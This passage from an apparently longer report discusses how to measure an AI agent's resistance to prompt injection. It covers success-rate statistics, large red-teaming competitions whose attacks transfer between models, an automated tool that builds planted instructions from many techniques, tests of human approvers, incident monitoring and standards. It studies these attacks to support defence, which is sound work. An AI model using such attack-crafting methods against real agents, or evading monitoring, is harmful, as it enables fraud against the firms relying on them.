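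The evidence that the tools repeat themselves is stronger than the evidence that repetition weakens training. The larger collection did worse in three of four comparisons, but two of those gaps were only one and two cases out of 40, and in the fourth comparison it did better by one case. Zorz also notes that the researchers chose cases where simple attacks had already broken the unprotected model, so the rates don't describe ordinary use.

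For a security test, repetition makes the upper bound too optimistic. Suppose 3,000 failed attacks consist of 100 wordings for each of 30 strategies. Survey statisticians correct for such groups by calculating an effective number of attempts:

`n_eff = n / (1 + (m − 1)ρ)`

Here `m` is the number of attacks in each group, and `ρ` measures how similar their outcomes are, from 0 for unrelated to 1 for always the same. If `ρ` is 1, the 3,000 attacks count as 30, and the upper bound rises from 0.1% to about 10%. Even if `ρ` is 0.1, they count as about 275, and the bound is 1.1%. Testers can't estimate `ρ` when every attack has failed, so the cautious choice is to count each attack strategy once, however many texts use it.

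*AutoPI* (Damianakis and Psounis, 2026) recommends reporting the attack success rate together with technique coverage, the share of known techniques that produced at least one success. The tool it describes tries 132 ways of constructing a planted instruction, grouped into 34 techniques, and reworks the ones that fail. The paper cites a test in which Gemini 3.8 Flash resisted a general adaptive attacker in 60% of scenarios after 150 attempts. When the attacker used only turn injection, one of the techniques, the model resisted in 36%, so the general search had evidently not made full use of that technique. A vendor whose agent resists nearly every attack should therefore list the techniques that testers tried and how many attempts they made with each.

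A test of the invoice assistant also needs to cover different attacker goals, such as adding a new payee, raising an amount, causing a duplicate payment or sending the owner a misleading message. No test can include attack techniques that are invented after it is run.

### When attackers retry

If each attempt succeeds with probability `p`, the chance of at least one success in `k` independent attempts is `1 − (1 − p)^k`. When `p` is 0.1%, about 700 messages give the attacker an even chance of at least one success, and 3,000 give a 95% chance. A test with 3,000 failed attacks therefore gives little assurance if an attacker can send as many messages as the testers did. An attacker who instead sent one message to each of 3,000 firms would expect about three successes at the same rate.

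Measured rates often rise more slowly than the formula predicts. Claude Opus 4.5's rate of 4.7% for one attempt implies 38% after ten and 99% after a hundred, but the measured figures were 33.6% and 63.0%. In CAISI's tests with five goals, 25 attempts raised the average from 57% to 80%, whereas independent attempts would have raised it to nearly 100%. This is probably because some cases are much harder than others, and repetition helps little with the hardest. The formula gives an upper limit for an attacker who learns nothing between attempts, but an attacker who learns could exceed it. Vendors should therefore measure and report success after, for example, 1, 10 and 100 attempts per case.

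Attackers also reuse the attacks that work. *Security Challenges in AI Agent Deployment* describes a one-month competition in which participants made 1.8 million attempts against agents running on 22 models. Just over 60,000 succeeded, or about 3%. The organisers then used the data to build a benchmark whose attacks succeeded almost every time against all the agents tested.

An attacker can practise on one system before attacking another. Dziemian, Lin and colleagues (2026) analysed a later competition, hosted by the security company Gray Swan, in *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* According to CAISI's *Insights into AI Agent Security from a Large-Scale Red-Teaming Competition*, more than 400 participants made over 250,000 attempts and succeeded at least once against each of the 13 models. Attacks that worked on the more resistant models were particularly likely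 to work on weaker ones. A firm that blocks a sender after three suspicious messages therefore can't assume that the attacker has had only three tries. The participants attacked models, so these results suggest what could happen within the permissions an agent has been granted, but not whether a permission check would withstand an attack.

### Testing the people who approve

A field experiment on approval would add fake requests to people's ordinary work. Participants would agree beforehand to occasional tests but wouldn't know which requests were fake. Experienced fraud testers would write the requests and use accounts they control, so no money would be lost if someone approved one by mistake. The experiment would also measure how many honest requests people refuse, because a person could stop every fake request by refusing everything. Testers could randomly assign different approval prompts,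 for example with and without a warning that an account number appears only in an email.

If participants approve none of 60 fakes, the upper bound on their approval rate is 5%. If they approve two, the interval is about 1% to 11%, which neither confirms nor refutes the claim. The fakes also have to be rare, because people who expect one will look harder. If one request in 100 is fake, 60 fakes require 6,000 requests. At ten requests a week, a single firm would need more than eleven years, while a dozen firms would need about one. Even then, a dozen owners are a small sample, however many decisions each one makes. A vendor with many customers could run a large enough experiment.

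Confirming that the software asks for approval is not enough to show that a deployment is secure. The Frontier Model Forum's *Emerging Security Practices for AI Agents* (2026), from an industry body for AI developers, warns that prompts which users passively click through may create an "illusion of oversight". @IT's *ヒューマン・イン・ザ・ループ万能説崩壊 NISTが提唱するAIエージェント運用のあるべき姿* reports that in August 2026 NIST described an alternative to frequent prompts, in which someone approves a "flight plan" before the agent starts. An experiment would still have to test whether people notice a bad plan.

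### A year without incidents

The 3/n approximation also works for time. If the firm uses its assistant for one year without a loss, the 95% upper bound is three losses a year. If a thousand firms each went a year without a loss, the bound would fall to about one loss per firm every 330 years, but only against the attackers those firms faced.

A year without a successful attack proves little if few attackers tried. If five forged invoices reached the assistant and all five failed, the 95% upper confidence bound on the success rate is still 45%. If none arrived, the year provides no evidence about how well the assistant resists them.

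An incident record therefore needs to include the number of attempted attacks. The firm can't count attacks it failed to recognise, but it can run harmless test attacks and measure the share its monitoring detects. If the monitoring detects a share `d` of successful attacks, the upper bound on the attack success rate after `n` attacks with no recorded success is about `3/(nd)`. With 1,000 attacks and monitoring that detects half of the successes, the bound is 0.6%, compared with 0.3% if monitoring detected them all.

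Detection can also be slow. TechRadar reports that one of Anthropic's models sent a made-up tip to the Philadelphia police in July 2026 and nobody noticed for 72 days. OpenAI notified Australia of a breach 84 days after it happened. These cases arose while agents were being trained and evaluated, not from forged invoices, but a quiet theft could stay hidden just as long.

Official definitions also affect the count. In October 2026, NIST and two other US agencies published voluntary practices for handling incidents in which agents exceed their limits. The practices define an "SI control incident", where SI stands for "super intelligence", the US government's new term for AI. According to the National Law Review's *When the AI Agent Goes Off-Script*, the definition covers only significant actions that neither the operator nor an attacker instructed. If a forged invoice hijacks the assistant,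 the resulting payment doesn't count as a control incident, though it may still be an ordinary cybersecurity incident. The practices also define near-misses, and a firm could record its own, because when the check refuses a planted action, as CapScope did in 31 runs, it shows that an attack arrived and got past the model.

Small firms would benefit from pooling such records, because each one sees few attacks. MeriTalk's *NIST Outlines AI Incident-Response Road Map* reports that NIST plans to examine how organisations should log and share information about AI incidents, and to update its main guidance to cover cybersecurity incidents that involve AI systems.

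### What certificates and standards cover

Existing certificates mostly cover how an organisation manages its systems. Help Net Security's *How to use NIST and ISO frameworks to govern AI agents* (2026) explains that, for agents, ISO/IEC 42001, an international standard for managing AI, supports formal registration, periodic reviews and logs that link each action to an identity. NIST's AI Risk Management Framework similarly emphasises clear ownership and continuous attention to risk. These practices help an organisation keep grants narrow and record incidents. But an auditor could confirm that the firm reviews the assistant's permissions every quarter without testing whether a forged invoice would get paid.

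The Frontier Model Forum considers older standards, such as ISO/IEC 27001 and NIST's Cybersecurity Framework, still relevant to the infrastructure around an agent, but acknowledges that many agent security problems have no standard benchmarks or methods for adversarial testing. In January 2026, NIST's CAISI asked industry and researchers how to measure the security of agents (*CAISI Issues Request for Information About Securing AI Agent Systems*). According to ExecutiveGov, the priorities of the standards initiative that followed include research on agent security and identity.

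NIST's later work comes closer to the designs in this field. *Design Tenets for Agent Identity Management Systems*, by Booth and colleagues from NIST and the research organisation MITRE (2026), sets out ten principles, which Biometric Update summarises in *NIST sets 10 principles for AI agent identity and authorization*. Each agent should have its own identity, with minimal, temporary and revocable access. Its permissions should be separate from its decisions about what to try, and it should not be able to alter the record of its actions. NIST acknowledges that current standards and technology don't fully meet every principle.

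The principles address confused deputies by combining delegation, least privilege, separate policies and deterministic access decisions. Identity alone would not be enough, because an invoice assistant with its own identity could still make the same mistake as Hardy's compiler.

| Scheme | What it covers | What it leaves open |
|---|---|---|
| ISO/IEC 42001 | Ownership, reviews and logs | Whether attacks succeed |
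| ISO/IEC 27001 and NIST's Cybersecurity Framework | Security of the surrounding infrastructure | What a hijacked model can do with permitted tools |
| NIST's ten principles for agent identity | Identity, limited access and reliable records | Whether a particular grant is narrow enough and whether users approve frauds |
| The October 2026 incident practices | Uninstructed actions by agents, mainly in training and evaluation | Actions caused by prompt injection |

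None of these schemes would establish all five claims. ExecutiveGov's *NIST, NSA, CISA Issue AI Incident Response Practices* describes a NIST programme that tests models on hidden data, and a future certificate could similarly use hidden attacks. Vendors couldn't train their agents on those attacks, although testers would still need to adapt them to each defence. The certificate would also have to name the model, tools and grant that the testers examined, because a new model could change the measured success rates and a new tool could open a route around the check.
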